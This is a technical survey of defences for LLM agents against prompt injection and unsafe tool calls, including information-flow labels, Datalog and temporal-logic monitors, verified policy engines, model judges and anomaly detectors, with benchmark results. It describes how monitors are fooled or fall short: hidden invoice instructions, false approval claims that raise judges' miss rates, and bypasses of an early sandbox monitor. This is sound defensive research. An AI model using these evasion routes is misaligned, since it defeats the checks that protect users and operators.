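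*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) explains that the plans use a restricted form of the programming language Python. A simplified plan for the employee's request could look like this:

```
invoice  = read_mail(sender="supplier", date="yesterday")
total    = quarantined_model("Find the total in euros", invoice)
dollars  = convert_currency(total, "EUR", "USD")
contract = read_file("contracts/supplier.pdf")
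answer   = quarantined_model("Do they agree?", total, contract)
```

The hidden instruction reaches only the quarantined model. The instruction can't add a `send_mail` call because the privileged model finished the plan before the quarantined model read the invoice. It can still make the quarantined model return a false total, and the interpreter has to check its policy to determine whether the converter may receive that value.

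CaMeL guarantees that untrusted text can't add steps to the plan or send data anywhere the policy forbids, provided that the user's request is trustworthy, the policy is correct and the interpreter has no flaws. *Operationalizing CaMeL* warns that several Python features make data flows hard to analyse, and recommends a simpler language designed for security.

The available results differ on how useful CaMeL is. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* reports that it stops nearly all AgentDojo attacks with comparable task success. Zhang and colleagues tested their own adaptation of CaMeL, which completed only 18.4% to 30.6% of AgentDojo tasks, depending on the model, compared with 65.3% to 87.8% without a defence. Attacks against the adapted version succeeded in at most 0.2% of cases. On AgentDyn, it completed no tasks with any of the four models.

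Zhang and colleagues were testing a competitor to their own system, and their adaptation may have contributed to these failures. But a plan written in advance is poorly suited to tasks where the agent must read something before it knows what to do next. Neither source gives figures for CaMeL's cost.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) proposes a looser separation. A model that has read untrusted text may still call tools, and the software blocks only the calls that its labels prohibit.

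### FIDES hides values from the planner

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, lets the model plan as it goes but hides data that would make the context's label stricter. With the supplier's invoice, it works as follows:

1. `read_mail` returns the invoice, which has a stricter label than the context. FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planning model only a name, such as `#read_mail_0`.
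2. The planning model has a quarantined model extract the total. FIDES stores the answer in another variable.
3. The planning model uses that variable's name as an argument for `convert_currency`.
4. FIDES replaces the name with the value, checks the labels and makes the call if the policy allows it.

The planning model never sees the invoice, so the context remains trusted. A policy can therefore require that untrusted text did not influence a message's recipient, while allowing such text in the body. The employee could then have a summary of the invoice sent to the finance department, although the summary might include any false bank details from the invoice.

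If the planning model needs information from the hidden text, it can request an answer in a restricted format. A yes-or-no answer can carry only one bit of information from the attacker, so a policy may accept it even for a consequential call. An unrestricted text answer could carry a whole new instruction, so it is still treated more strictly.

With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every AgentDojo attack. Attacks succeeded without the policy checks, so hiding the data isn't enough on its own. With the checks on, FIDES completed 8% more tasks than a basic planner when both used GPT-4o, and 16% more when both used OpenAI's o1. Newer models have since replaced GPT-4o and o1. The mechanism itself reduces task success, which was 6.3% lower than the basic planner's when neither system checked a policy. The extra calls to a quarantined model also take time and money, but the headline results don't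 include figures for either.

Costa and colleagues prove that label tracking can enforce a property called explicit secrecy. Take two sets of stored data, *d₁* and *d₂*, that contain the same public information but different secrets. Let *g* be the effect of one particular sequence of tool calls. Explicit secrecy requires that

*if d₁ and d₂ agree on all public data, then g(d₁) and g(d₂) do too.*

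An observer who sees only public data therefore can't learn a secret from what those calls write, but may still learn something from which calls the agent makes. If the assistant contacts the currency converter only when the contract contains a penalty clause, the converter's developer can infer that the clause exists. Preventing this would require blocking nearly every public action after the agent has read anything secret.

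The proof assumes that the model always gives the same output for the same input, and it doesn't cover information leaked through signals such as timing. The system's threat model also treats tool descriptions as trusted. In MCP, an outside developer writes the converter's description, so a poisoned description could influence the planner without changing the context's label. The host would have to check tool descriptions separately or label them as untrusted.

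### FORGE follows data through a graph

FORGE, the system behind Palumbo and colleagues' formal guarantee, records each message, tool call and result as a point in a graph. An arrow connects two points if the earlier one may have influenced the later one. The graph can include several agents, so FORGE can follow text from an agent that reads mail to one that sends mail.

Policies are written in Datalog, a logic language in which a rule can refer to itself. The text after `:-` is the condition:

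```
Tainted(e) :- UntrustedInput(e).
Tainted(e) :- DependsOn(e, x), Tainted(x).

HasSecret(e) :- SensitiveInput(e).
HasSecret(e) :- DependsOn(e, x), HasSecret(x).

Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
```

The second rule marks an event as tainted if it depends on another tainted event. FORGE can apply this rule repeatedly to trace influence back through any number of steps. The last rule blocks a message from being sent outside if it depends on both untrusted text and sensitive data, as the one that forwards the contract does.

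This graph alone doesn't solve the labelling problem, because FORGE treats each model response as dependent on all the messages the model received. The researchers therefore wrote a second policy for individual actions and their arguments, which checks whether the user requested the action and whether its target came from an acceptable source. Under this policy, the assistant could send the supplier a question at the employee's request, even after reading the invoice.

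An experiment on AgentDojo compared this provenance policy with a FIDES-style label policy. The agent used GPT-4o and received the user's request again after each set of tool results. Repeating the request is itself a simple defence.

| Additional defence | Task success without an attack | Task success during an attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% |
| A model preselects the tools | 73.4% | 69.5% | 3.1% |
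| FIDES-style label policy | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.6% |
| Provenance policy | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.9% |

Agents completed nearly twice as many tasks under the provenance policy as under the label policy, with similar security. But the comparison used AgentDojo's own agent rather than the FIDES planner, so the label policy's low task success may reflect the use of plain labels without hidden variables. Agents completed more tasks with preselected tools than under either policy, so preselection might be the better choice where an occasional successful attack does little harm.

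The average run took 5.93 seconds without either policy, 7.70 seconds with the provenance policy and 10.18 seconds with the label policy. The researchers did not record the cost of model use in this test. In a smaller test with GPT-4.1 mini, FORGE stopped all five attempts to steal a secret document, at an average cost of less than half a cent per scenario. All five attempts succeeded when the agent had only a written instruction not to leak data.

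FORGE guarantees that an action never runs if the policy denies it. This requires every relevant action to pass through the monitor and the graph to correctly record every relevant event and influence. If the graph is missing an arrow that links the invoice to an email, FORGE can allow the email without breaking its formal rule.

### ActGov checks where each argument came from

ActGov describes every proposed call with a fixed set of records, including one for where each argument came from. For a bank transfer, the records might show that the employee supplied the amount but an outside email supplied the account number. Software fills in some records directly, and a language model fills in those that require understanding text, choosing from a fixed list of values. Ordinary program code then applies the policy.

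Another model drafts the policy before the agent goes into use. Z3, an SMT solver like the one in Progent, searches for a record *r* and a decision *v* such that

*r is possible, the policy gives the decision v, and r and v together violate a safety requirement.*

If the solver finds a combination of records for which the policy fails a stated requirement, the developers revise the policy. If the solver proves that no such combination exists, the policy meets the stated requirements for every possible combination. The proof doesn't show that the model will fill in the records correctly or that the requirements cover every danger.

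Zhang and colleagues tested four models. These are the results for DeepSeek-V4-Pro, the newest of DeepSeek's models in the comparison:

| Defence | AgentDojo: task success / attack success | AgentDyn: task success / attack success |
|---|---|---|
| None | 87.8% / 6.1% | 76.7% / 8.6% |
| ActGov | 75.5% / 0.0% | 60.0% / 0.7% |
| Progent | 81.6% / 0.8% | 21.7% / 1.4% |
| Adapted CaMeL | 20.4% / 0.0% | 0.0% / 0.0% |

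The task figures are for runs without an attack. Across all four models, no AgentDojo attacks succeeded against ActGov, and at most 0.7% of AgentDyn attacks did. The other models were Qwen3.6-Flash, MiniMax-M2.5 and GPT-4o mini, which OpenAI has long since replaced. The researchers don't report running costs.

ActGov had an advantage because its developers wrote its policies using half of the attack cases, with human review, and tested it on the other half. When they applied the AgentDojo policies to AgentDyn, task success fell from 60.0% to 10.0%. When they applied the AgentDyn policies to AgentDojo, it fell from 75.5% to 22.4%. No attacks succeeded in either test, but an employer would need many examples of its own employees' work to get a useful policy.

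### Over-blocking, labelling and hidden influence

Every defence in these comparisons reduced the number of tasks agents completed, sometimes drastically. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out that agents may have good reasons to follow outside instructions, such as those in a software manual, or to release some confidential information. It suggests that signed documents from known authors could receive less restrictive labels, although a signed invoice, like a signed tool definition, can still be unsafe.

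Someone also has to assign the original labels. FIDES accepts a label for each field of a tool's result, so the mail server could mark a message's date as trusted and its text as untrusted. An ordinary MCP server may not supply labels, although there are proposals for trust annotations. The host also can't rely on labels from the currency converter, because a malicious developer would mark everything as trusted. The safe default is to label all outside data as untrusted, but this again causes over-blocking.

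An attacker can also do harm without causing any forbidden call. Suppose the invoice falsely claims that the contract permits a 20% surcharge. The quarantined model may then report that the total is correct, leading the employee to overpay. In their standard design, Costa and colleagues check policies only before tool calls and treat answers to the user as harmless. Palumbo and colleagues' monitor didn't check final answers either. Once the researchers stopped counting blocked calls as successful attacks, the remaining successes all involved the agent's written answer.

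*From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) emphasises that untrusted text can influence an action even if none of its words appear in the result. In *Ghost in the Agent*, Cai and Wen (2026) built NeuroTaint to trace such influence through paraphrases, decisions and memories that an agent keeps between sessions. They report that it found far more connections than a FIDES-style tracker in 400 scenarios from 20 agent frameworks. NeuroTaint works offline, so it can help investigators explain a leak but can't stop a call.

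Tracing meaning usually requires a model, which can make mistakes. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) limits this dependence by using ordinary code to track which confidential records may have influenced an outgoing message. A model then compares the message with those records to detect paraphrases and coded references. The agent can't bypass this check, but the checking model may still miss a disguised secret. ActGov has a similar weakness. If its model wrongly records that an account number from the invoice came from the employee, the verified policy may allow the payment.

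## Rules about the order of actions, and what a monitor can enforce

Data labels let a host track where information came from, but other rules depend on what the agent has already done. Suppose a shop's customer service agent is allowed to pay a refund only after checking the customer's identity. The call `refund(order=17)` looks the same whether or not the check took place, so an enforcement point that examines only this call can't determine whether to allow it. It needs the run's history, which researchers call a trace.

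### A rule with memory

Temporal logic extends ordinary logic with operators for time. Past-time operators refer only to what has already happened, so a monitor can evaluate them before it lets a call through. Three are common:

- PREVIOUS *p*: *p* was true at the preceding event.
- ONCE *p*: *p* was true at some earlier event.
- *p* SINCE *q*: *q* was true at some earlier event, and *p* has been true ever since.

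ONCE is enough for "refund only after an identity check", but the agent might then switch to a different customer. A stricter rule allows a refund only if an identity check has succeeded and the agent hasn't switched customers since:

*refund → (¬switch SINCE verified)*

The arrow means "only if" and ¬ means "not". The monitor doesn't have to search the whole trace each time. It can store a single true-or-false value *V*, which starts as false, and update it after each call:

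*Vₙ = verifiedₙ ∨ (¬switchₙ ∧ Vₙ₋₁)*

Here ∨ means "or" and ∧ means "and". The monitor allows a refund if *V* is true just before the call.

| Call | *V* before | Decision | *V* after |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. `check_identity`, which succeeds | False | Allowed, because the rule limits only refunds | True |
| 2. `refund(order=17)` | True | Allowed | True |
| 3. `switch_customer` | True | Allowed | False |
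| 4. `refund(order=17)` | False | Denied | False |

Calls 2 and 4 are identical, but the monitor treats them differently. Under the simpler ONCE rule, it would have allowed both.

A practical rule also has to connect the identity check to the purchase being refunded. Otherwise a customer could prove their own identity and collect a refund for someone else's purchase.

### Agent-C checks a call during generation

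Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, describe Agent-C, which applies such rules before a call leaves the model's generation process. A developer writes rules such as "before reading an order, the agent must have looked up a user, and that user must own the order". Agent-C then works as follows:

1. The model generates a tool's name and arguments, and Agent-C checks that each argument has the right type.
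2. Agent-C looks up any facts the rules need, such as the order's owner, in the tool's own data.
3. It adds the proposed call to the trace and translates the trace and the rules into logical formulas.
4. An SMT solver checks whether the run could still continue in a way that satisfies every rule.
5. If it could, Agent-C releases the call. Otherwise, it discards the call and has the model generate another.

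With an open-weight model, Agent-C can go back to the start of the call without processing the prompt again. Commercial providers don't give outsiders the necessary access to token probabilities, so Agent-C has to resend the whole prompt, which costs more. After a set number of failed attempts, Agent-C gives the model an error message.

One rule in the tests required refunds to go to the original payment method or a gift card. Claude Sonnet 4.5 had this rule in its instructions but still tried to send a refund to a different account when the customer insisted. Agent-C compared the account with the shop's records and blocked the call.

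Kamath and colleagues used τ-bench, the customer service benchmark, with 115 retail and 50 airline tasks:

| Model | Compliance with the policy, without and with Agent-C | Task success, without and with Agent-C |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 77.4% and 100% | 71.8% and 75.2% |
| GPT-5 | 83.7% and 100% | 66.1% and 70.6% |

For open-weight models, average compliance was 37.8% without a guardrail, 82.3% with AgentSpec and 100% with Agent-C. The researchers count a task as successful only if the agent also followed the policy. This puts the unguarded agents at a disadvantage, so some of the gain in task success may come from the scoring. They also wrote 34 tasks in which the customer pursued a forbidden goal, and Agent-C prevented the harmful actions in all of them.

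### LeanGuard checks the monitor with a theorem prover

A monitor's own code may contain mistakes. In *LEANGUARD*, Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026) wrote their monitor in Lean 4, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. They proved that, for every possible history, the monitor's decision matches a separate logical definition of the policy. Lean checks this proof once, when the developer builds the policy, so individual calls don't need their own proofs.

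LeanGuard allows a call if

*(at least one permit applies) ∧ (every requirement holds) ∧ (no prohibition applies) ∧ (no evaluation error)*.

The last condition prevents a call from being allowed because data is missing. If an order's status is missing, a carelessly written program might assume that the order is not cancelled, but LeanGuard denies the call.

It can limit a temporal operator to a period of time, or to events that involve the same customer or order. It also records an allowed call before the tool runs, so if a refund request times out, the agent can't repeat it while the outcome is unknown.

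After denying a call, LeanGuard can tell the model which rules failed and give it a hint, such as asking the customer for confirmation. It can also search for a similar call and prove that the policy allows it. For example, if an account has spent 60 units of a 100-unit budget, the search could reduce a request for 70 units to 40. A developer has to specify which changes preserve the user's intention. The working system doesn't use these repairs yet, and the researchers tested them only on recorded denials.

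Sankar and colleagues ran five Qwen models, with 0.8 to 27 billion parameters, on 278 customer service tasks from τ²-bench. Without a guard, the agents carried out at least 33 forbidden calls in 28 of 1,390 runs. Seventeen of these calls broke a rule about earlier events or their order. The true number may be higher because the recordings don't show whether the customer had consented. With LeanGuard, the agents carried out no forbidden calls, as the design guarantees.

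| Result | No guard | Denial only | Denial with feedback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Task success | 72.7% | 68.9% | 70.9% |
| Blocked calls | None | 983 | 719 |
| Denied actions the agent later completed correctly | None | 34 of 620 | 48 of 526 |

Task success was lower with feedback. The overall drop isn't statistically significant, but retail success fell from 73.9% to 66.0%. The proof-based search found a permitted alternative for 88 of the 252 denials caused by argument values, usually within a few milliseconds. Most of these alternatives sent a refund to the original payment method.

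The researchers also tested Progent, which checks calls against limits on their arguments. Forbidden calls took effect in 2.6% of runs with Progent and 2.0% of runs without a guard, a difference that could be due to chance. More than half of the violations under Progent broke rules about earlier events or their order. The comparison favours LeanGuard because the researchers counted violations of LeanGuard's own rules.

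On DTap, a collection of attacks on agents, LeanGuard reduced the success rate of direct prompt injection, in which the malicious instruction is in the request to the agent, from 57.9% to 5.9%. For indirect prompt injection, in which the instruction is in other data the agent reads, the rate fell from 22.3% to 3.8%.

However, the agents in these tests were only allowed to read data. Success on harmless tasks fell from 53.1% to 12.5%, since many required the agent to book, buy or change something. The results are more encouraging for telephone company tasks, which rarely involved changes. The success rate of direct attacks there fell from 55.1% to 2.4%, while success on harmless tasks stayed at about 75%.

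LeanGuard allowed no call that changed anything in any of the 289 attack runs that still succeeded. The harm was in the agent's written answer, which LeanGuard doesn't check. For example, the agent gave a false diagnosis or misreported a bill.

### Tether follows what a command does

Agent-C and LeanGuard need to know what each tool does, which the text of a shell command often doesn't reveal. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, a paper mainly from Google DeepMind, use an example with three commands:

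| Command | Label of the report afterwards | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| Upload `report.txt` to an outside website | Public | Allowed |
| Copy a confidential inventory into `report.txt` | Sensitive | Allowed |
| Upload `report.txt` to the same website | Sensitive | Denied |

The two upload commands are identical, and neither names the inventory. Tether can distinguish them because it keeps a data label for each file. It handles a command in five steps:

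1. It runs the command in a disposable sandbox, where changes to files don't affect the real ones.
2. It records the command's requests to the operating system, and a proxy holds back any outgoing network request.
3. It translates these records into simple actions, such as "copy this file" or "upload this file".
4. A policy engine written in Lean 4 checks the actions against the labels and the rules.
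5. If the policy allows them, Tether makes the file changes permanent and releases the network requests. Otherwise, it discards them.

Tether can't determine exactly how a program uses the data it reads. So if a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats the second file as containing information from the first. This avoids missed leaks but can cause false alarms.

The researchers proved general properties of the engine. For example, adding a permissive rule can't cancel another rule's denial. They also proved seven statements about their test policy that hold for runs of any length, including that secret data never reaches an outside host. A language model may write such proofs because Lean rejects any proof that contains an error.

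The tests replayed recorded runs from two collections of programming and system administration tasks. The comparison system, Claude Code's Auto Mode, has a language model review each command.

| Monitor | Attack runs blocked (of 344) | Harmless runs blocked (of 1,590) |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 100% | 4.7% |
| Auto Mode with its default rules | 91.6% | 9.7% |
| Auto Mode with Tether's policy | 89.2% | 3.5% |

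These figures cover only runs in which Tether could model every action, so they exclude runs that used background processes or databases. Tether can be set to block both entirely. The researchers also refined their policy using runs from the benchmarks, so Tether might block more harmless work elsewhere. Of the 74 false alarms, 17 came from commands that opened secret files by accident, such as a text search through every folder.

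In a wider analysis, Sistla and colleagues found that 28.2% of the runs from one collection and 22.1% from the other required a judgement about content. For example, an agent might put harmful code in a file it has permission to edit. Tether can't detect this from how data moves.

### Safety properties and Schneider's theorem

Some rules are impossible to enforce by blocking actions, however good the monitor is. The theory depends on a technical term, the safety property. A rule is a safety property if every violation becomes visible after a finite number of steps and nothing that happens later can repair it. If *P* is the set of runs that obey the rule, then for every run *x*:

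*x ∉ P ⇒ there is an n such that, for every continuation y, x₁…xₙy ∉ P*

The refund rule is a safety property because once the agent has paid a refund without first checking identity, no later check can undo the violation.

*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) examined monitors that watch a program and stop it before it breaks a rule. According to Basin's (2012) summary of the result, such monitors can enforce only safety properties. A monitor must base each decision on the steps observed so far, so it cannot tell when to intervene if violations of a rule never show up in those steps.

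"Every deletion is eventually backed up" is what computer scientists call a liveness property, a requirement that something eventually happens. If an agent deletes a file without a backup, it may still make one from another copy tomorrow. A monitor that blocks the deletion may therefore stop a run that would have obeyed the rule, but a monitor that allows it can't ensure that the backup follows.

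A developer can often replace a rule that a monitor can't enforce with a stricter one that it can. For example, "Delete a file only after backing it up" is a safety property, and a monitor can enforce it with the temporal operator ONCE. Adding a deadline is less useful. If the rule is "Back up every deleted file within an hour", a monitor can detect a violation after an hour, but it can prevent one only by making the backup itself.

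Agent-C lets developers write rules about later actions, but the same limit applies. It can check that a backup is still possible, but it can't force the model to request one. If the model tries to finish without the backup, Agent-C ends the run in an error state. Its proof of compliance covers only runs that end without this error.

### What edit automata add

An edit automaton is a model of a monitor that can suppress actions and insert others, whereas Schneider's monitors can only stop the program. It could enforce the original backup rule as follows:

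1. The agent requests a deletion, and the monitor holds it back.
2. The agent continues with other work.
3. If the agent requests the backup, the monitor carries out both actions.
4. If the agent never requests it, the monitor never carries out the deletion.

Every run this produces obeys the rule, even though the rule isn't a safety property. The method works only if the action can be delayed. A tool-using agent often needs one call's result before it can choose the next, so the host would have to tell the model that the deletion is still pending.

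### The 2026 theory for tool-using agents

In July 2026, Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, examined four ways in which agents depart from the classical theory:

| Difference | Example | Consequence |
|---|---|---|
| Fallible judgements | A model has to decide whether an email contains personal data | The monitor must accept some missed violations or some false alarms |
| Irreversible effects | Nobody can recall a completed payment | The monitor can enforce fewer rules than an edit automaton |
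| Unbounded data | A rule limits payments to any number of recipients | No program can analyse every possible policy |
| Steered proposals | An invoice influences both the agent and the judging model | A guarantee based on ordinary examples may fail |

**Irreversible effects.** Ray first assumes that the monitor always gets correct answers to the questions in its policy. He proves that such a monitor can enforce exactly those safety properties whose violations it can recognise with its memory. Enforcing a property here means preventing every violation without changing any run that obeys the rules. Such properties include a daily limit on transfers to each recipient and a ban on sending mail after the user withdraws access.

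If permitted calls must go ahead immediately, as Ray requires, a monitor can't enforce the rule "every payment is eventually confirmed", because it has to allow or block the payment before any confirmation could arrive. A host that can delay payments could still use the edit automaton's method.

**Unbounded data.** A developer may want to know whether a set of rules could ever block anything. Ray proves that no program can answer this for every set of rules if the rules may use two counters that can go up, go down and be tested for zero. A program can answer it if counters only go up and rules only compare them with fixed limits. Such rules can still express the daily transfer limit.

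**Fallible judgements.** Suppose a run has up to 20 calls, and the employer wants at most 5% of runs to contain a violation. A simple method divides the 5% among the calls, so the judging model may miss at most 0.25% of violations at each call. Conformal calibration, a statistical method, uses known violations to set the judge's threshold. The guarantee holds on average over many runs and samples of known violations, and only if future violations resemble the known ones.

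Ray tested 23 judging models on 132 short instructions from AgentDojo, 35 of them harmful. With a target of 5% missed violations, every judge had to block everything. This result is weak evidence about the judges' quality, because each calibration used only 17 or 18 harmful examples and the method needs at least 19 to certify that target. With a 10% target, Gemma 2 9B blocked 78% of the harmless instructions.

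**Steered proposals.** An attacker may also change the text that the judge reads. If this can raise the miss rate at each call by at most *η*, the risk for a run of *H* calls with an original target of *δ* is at most

*δ + Hη*.

For 20 calls and a 5% target, an increase of one percentage point per call raises the limit to 25%. In Ray's test, a short false claim that an administrator had approved the action raised the miss rates of 8 of 11 judges by 20 to 60 percentage points, which is too much for the formula to give a useful guarantee.

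Blocking a call can also change what the agent does next. Ray constructs two systems that behave identically until a monitor blocks something, after which one stops and the other makes a new harmful request. Recordings of unguarded agents therefore can't show how well a monitor will work in use. This limit also applies to Tether's replayed runs.

He also ran an agent with a live monitor on 949 AgentDojo cases. A 3-billion-parameter judge reduced attack success from 4.7% to 0.4%, but it stopped 78% of calls, and task success fell from 25.4% to 18.0%. He separately compared 389 cases with and without this judge, and found that 34 attacks succeeded only without it and five succeeded only with it.

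In Ray's paper, "certified" can mean that the monitor enforces a rule in every run, provided that it gets correct answers to the policy's questions. It can also mean that the average risk stays within a limit under stated statistical assumptions. Neither meaning implies that the agent is safe in general, and Ray doesn't claim that any one theorem covers all four differences.

### What a proof leaves unproved

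A proof about the engine doesn't show that the policy is right. For LeanGuard, a language model drafted the rules from the benchmark's written policies, and people corrected them. The rules cover only requirements that a check on tool calls can enforce. Two of the 45 rules were stricter than the written policies, and those two alone stopped 164 calls. Tether's proofs also cover the policy, but they show only that it meets requirements that people have to choose.

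Tools may also behave differently from what the policy assumes. On DTap, LeanGuard relied on reviewed descriptions of what 199 tools do, so it would miss an effect a description leaves out, such as postmark-mcp's hidden recipient. Tether observes what local programs actually do, but not what happens on a remote server.

Finally, the monitor's record may be incomplete. Early versions of Tether missed some ways of moving data, such as hard links, which give a file a second name. An agent instructed to bypass Tether succeeded in 40% of attempts against an early version and in none after the researchers fixed the gaps those attempts revealed. The proofs about the policy engine could not have exposed these gaps, because they cover only the actions the engine receives.

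LeanGuard's proof likewise takes as given a record that the customer has approved an action, and doesn't cover how a conversation is turned into that record. In the customer service tests, a language model simulated the confirmation screen, and an audit found that some of the confirmations it recorded were wrong.

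## Detectors and audit logs

The message with the false bank details fits the employer's mail policy and breaks no rule about the order of calls, but a detector might still stop it. Detectors estimate how likely a text or an action is to be harmful and raise an alarm when the estimate crosses a threshold. A stricter threshold catches more attacks but also causes more false alarms. An evaluation therefore needs both the detection rate (the share of attacks that raise an alarm) and the false alarm rate (the share of harmless cases that do).

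| Detector | What it reads | What it outputs | Who sets the threshold |
|---|---|---|---|
| Injection classifier | A tool result, before the agent's model reads it | A score or a warning | Usually the vendor |
| Model judge | A proposed call and parts of the conversation | Allow or block | The vendor, through the judge's instructions |
| Anomaly detector | A sequence of calls | A score for how unusual it is | The operator |
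| ProbGuard | The current state, as a list of true-or-false facts | The probability that the run stays safe | The user |

### Classifiers for injected text

An injection classifier is a model trained on examples to tell injected instructions from ordinary text. The host runs it on each tool result, such as the supplier's invoice, and can then withhold the text, pass it on, or pass it on with a warning. A scanner of tool definitions can't detect injected instructions in the invoice because it never receives tool results.

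Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has such a classifier in its auto mode, a setting in which models decide whether to allow calls that the user would otherwise have to approve. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the classifier scans files, web pages and other tool results. If the text looks like an attempt to take over the agent, the classifier adds a warning to the context. The agent still reads the text, so the warning works only if the model heeds it. In Shaikh and Montaruli's tests, Claude Sonnet 5 sometimes identified an injection but still made the harmful call.

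Anthropic gives no separate detection rate for this classifier, but it commissioned an outside company, Trajectory Labs, to test auto mode as a whole. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports the results. Trajectory Labs ran 72 scenarios with hidden instructions ten times each, and Anthropic had no access to the scenarios beforehand.

| Agent | Attack success without extra checks | With extra checks |
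|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with Anthropic's latest models | 0.09% on average | 0% |
| Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, with GPT-5.6 Sol | 19.03% | 5.83% |

The Claude models resisted nearly every attack without help, so the test shows little about what auto mode added. The Codex result is more informative, because OpenAI's comparable checks prevented more than two thirds of the attacks that had succeeded without them. Trajectory Labs used attacks tuned to an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, and OpenAI has since updated its checks.

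### A second model as judge

Auto mode also has a model judge, which decides on each risky call before it runs:

1. Fixed rules let through calls that can't change anything, as well as edits to files inside the project folder.
2. For other calls, the judge receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It doesn't receive the agent's explanations or any tool results.
3. In the first stage, the judge gives a one-word answer under an instruction to block in case of doubt.
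4. If that answer is to block, the judge reasons through the same input and makes the final decision.
5. The agent receives the reason for a refusal and can try something else. After three refusals in a row or twenty in a session, Claude Code turns to the user.

Anthropic withholds the agent's explanations from the judge so that the agent can't talk it into a bad decision, and withholds tool results because they may contain injected text. This addresses the weakness Ray found, where a false claim of approval made most judges miss far more harmful calls. But the judge then can't tell where a call's arguments came from. If the employee asked the assistant to send the supplier's payment details to the finance department, the judge would have no sign that the account number was false.

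The judge answers yes or no, so users have no score to adjust. They can edit three parts of its instructions: what counts as trusted, which actions to block and which exceptions to allow. Tests of the judge have produced very different results:

| Test | Who ran it | Harmful actions missed | Harmless actions blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| 52 real cases in which an agent overstepped its task | Anthropic | 17% | 0.4% of 10,000 real calls |
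| 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data | Anthropic | 5.7% | The same 0.4% |
| Dangerous commands from a study with 1,053 paid testers | Anthropic, through a research vendor | 11% | Not reported |
| Synthetic attacks inserted into real coding runs | Apollo Research, with Anthropic | 12%, then 7% after changes | Not reported |
| 253 actions near the limit of the user's permission | A separate stress test | 81.0% | 19.8% |

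The 17% corresponds to about nine missed actions, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%. It also reflects Anthropic's choice of threshold, which allows more misses in return for fewer interruptions. The first stage alone missed only 6.6% of these actions but blocked 8.5% of harmless calls.

Apollo's 7% includes attacks it had already shown to Anthropic. On attacks Anthropic had not seen, the improved judge caught about half of those the earlier version had missed, but missed about 2% of those the earlier version had caught.

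This report relies on a secondary account of the stress test, besthub.dev's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*. The test's designers deliberately placed permitted and forbidden targets next to each other. Part of the miss rate also comes from the rules in step 1, which let some actions through without sending them to the judge. Of the 160 actions in the category that does go to the judge, auto mode still missed 70.3% of the harmful ones and blocked 31.9% of the harmless ones. Sistla and colleagues used less ambiguous attacks in their comparison with Tether and found a miss rate of only 8.4%.

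These results suggest that the judge is much better at detecting danger than at determining what the user has permitted. Anthropic found the same pattern in most of the misses it examined. In one, the judge detected that a command would overwrite a project's history but treated "clean up the PR" as permission for it. *Ajar* (2026) also supports this, since auto mode allowed every tested call once the researchers put the instruction to make it in the user's message. Anthropic has since described a category of "hard denies", such as sending secrets to outsiders, that the judge should never approve, even at the user's request.

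Auto mode was the starting mode for interactive Claude Code sessions on every plan by 12 November 2026, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026). Anthropic's posts include no figures for the delay auto mode adds. In Yu and colleagues' airline tests, which used a different model judge, runs with the judge took much longer than runs with fixed rules.

### Anomaly detection over sequences of calls

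An anomaly detector learns what an agent's work normally looks like and scores departures from it. A simple version counts how often each call has followed another in past runs and estimates a probability *P* for each step. For a run with calls *c₁* to *cₙ*, it adds up

*score = −log P(c₂ | c₁) − … − log P(cₙ | cₙ₋₁)*,

so rare steps raise the score most. The operator chooses the score that triggers an alarm, often according to how many alarms the staff can investigate.

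An anomaly detector might give the office assistant a high score for opening a contract and then writing to a new outside address. An employee's first day on a new project might also produce a high score. A message to the finance department after reading an invoice would look normal, even if the message contained a fraudulent account number.

Little has been published on how well detectors identify unusual tool calls. The NSA recommends passing logs to an organisation's security monitoring system to look for unexpected calls and unusual message flows, but gives no detection rates. Yuan and colleagues list learned profiles of agent behaviour as future work for AEGIS. An organisation would have to measure false alarms on its own traffic before relying on such a detector.

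### Predicting unsafe states with ProbGuard

*ProbGuard* (Wang, Poskitt and colleagues, 2025) describes a monitor designed to raise an alarm before an agent does anything wrong. One example is a household robot that must not leave the kitchen for more than ten minutes while the stove is on.

1. An expert defines the unsafe state and the facts that matter, such as whether the stove is on and whether the robot is in the kitchen.
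2. ProbGuard converts recorded runs into sequences of states, each a combination of these facts, and counts how often one state follows another.
3. It estimates the probability of moving from state *i* to state *j* as *(nᵢⱼ + 1) / (nᵢ + kᵢ)*. Here *nᵢⱼ* is the number of times this happened, *nᵢ* is the number of recorded moves out of state *i*, and *kᵢ* is the number of possible next states. The added 1 keeps a possible but unrecorded move from getting a probability of zero.
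4. While the agent works, ProbGuard calculates the probability that the run will never reach the unsafe state. If this falls below the user's threshold *θ*, it stops the agent or adds a warning to the model's context.

The researchers tested it on household tasks with an agent based on GPT-4o mini:

| Response to an alarm | Unsafe runs | Completed tasks |
|---|---|---|
| No monitor | 40.63% | 59.38% |
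| Stop the agent, *θ* = 0.9 | 2.60% | 10.42% |
| Stop the agent, *θ* = 0.5 | 21.35% | 41.14% |
| Warn the model, *θ* = 0.9 | 14.07% | 47.74% |

Warning the model led to fewer unsafe runs and more completed tasks than stopping the agent at *θ* = 0.5. Each check took less than 50 milliseconds when the probabilities were calculated in advance.

In tests on driving software that doesn't use a language model, ProbGuard raised no false alarms at *θ* = 0.3, and its average warning time ranged from 0.01 to 15.84 seconds across seven scenarios. The false alarm rate was 75% at *θ* = 0.5 and 100% at *θ* = 0.7, the threshold that produced the longest reported warning time, 38.66 seconds.

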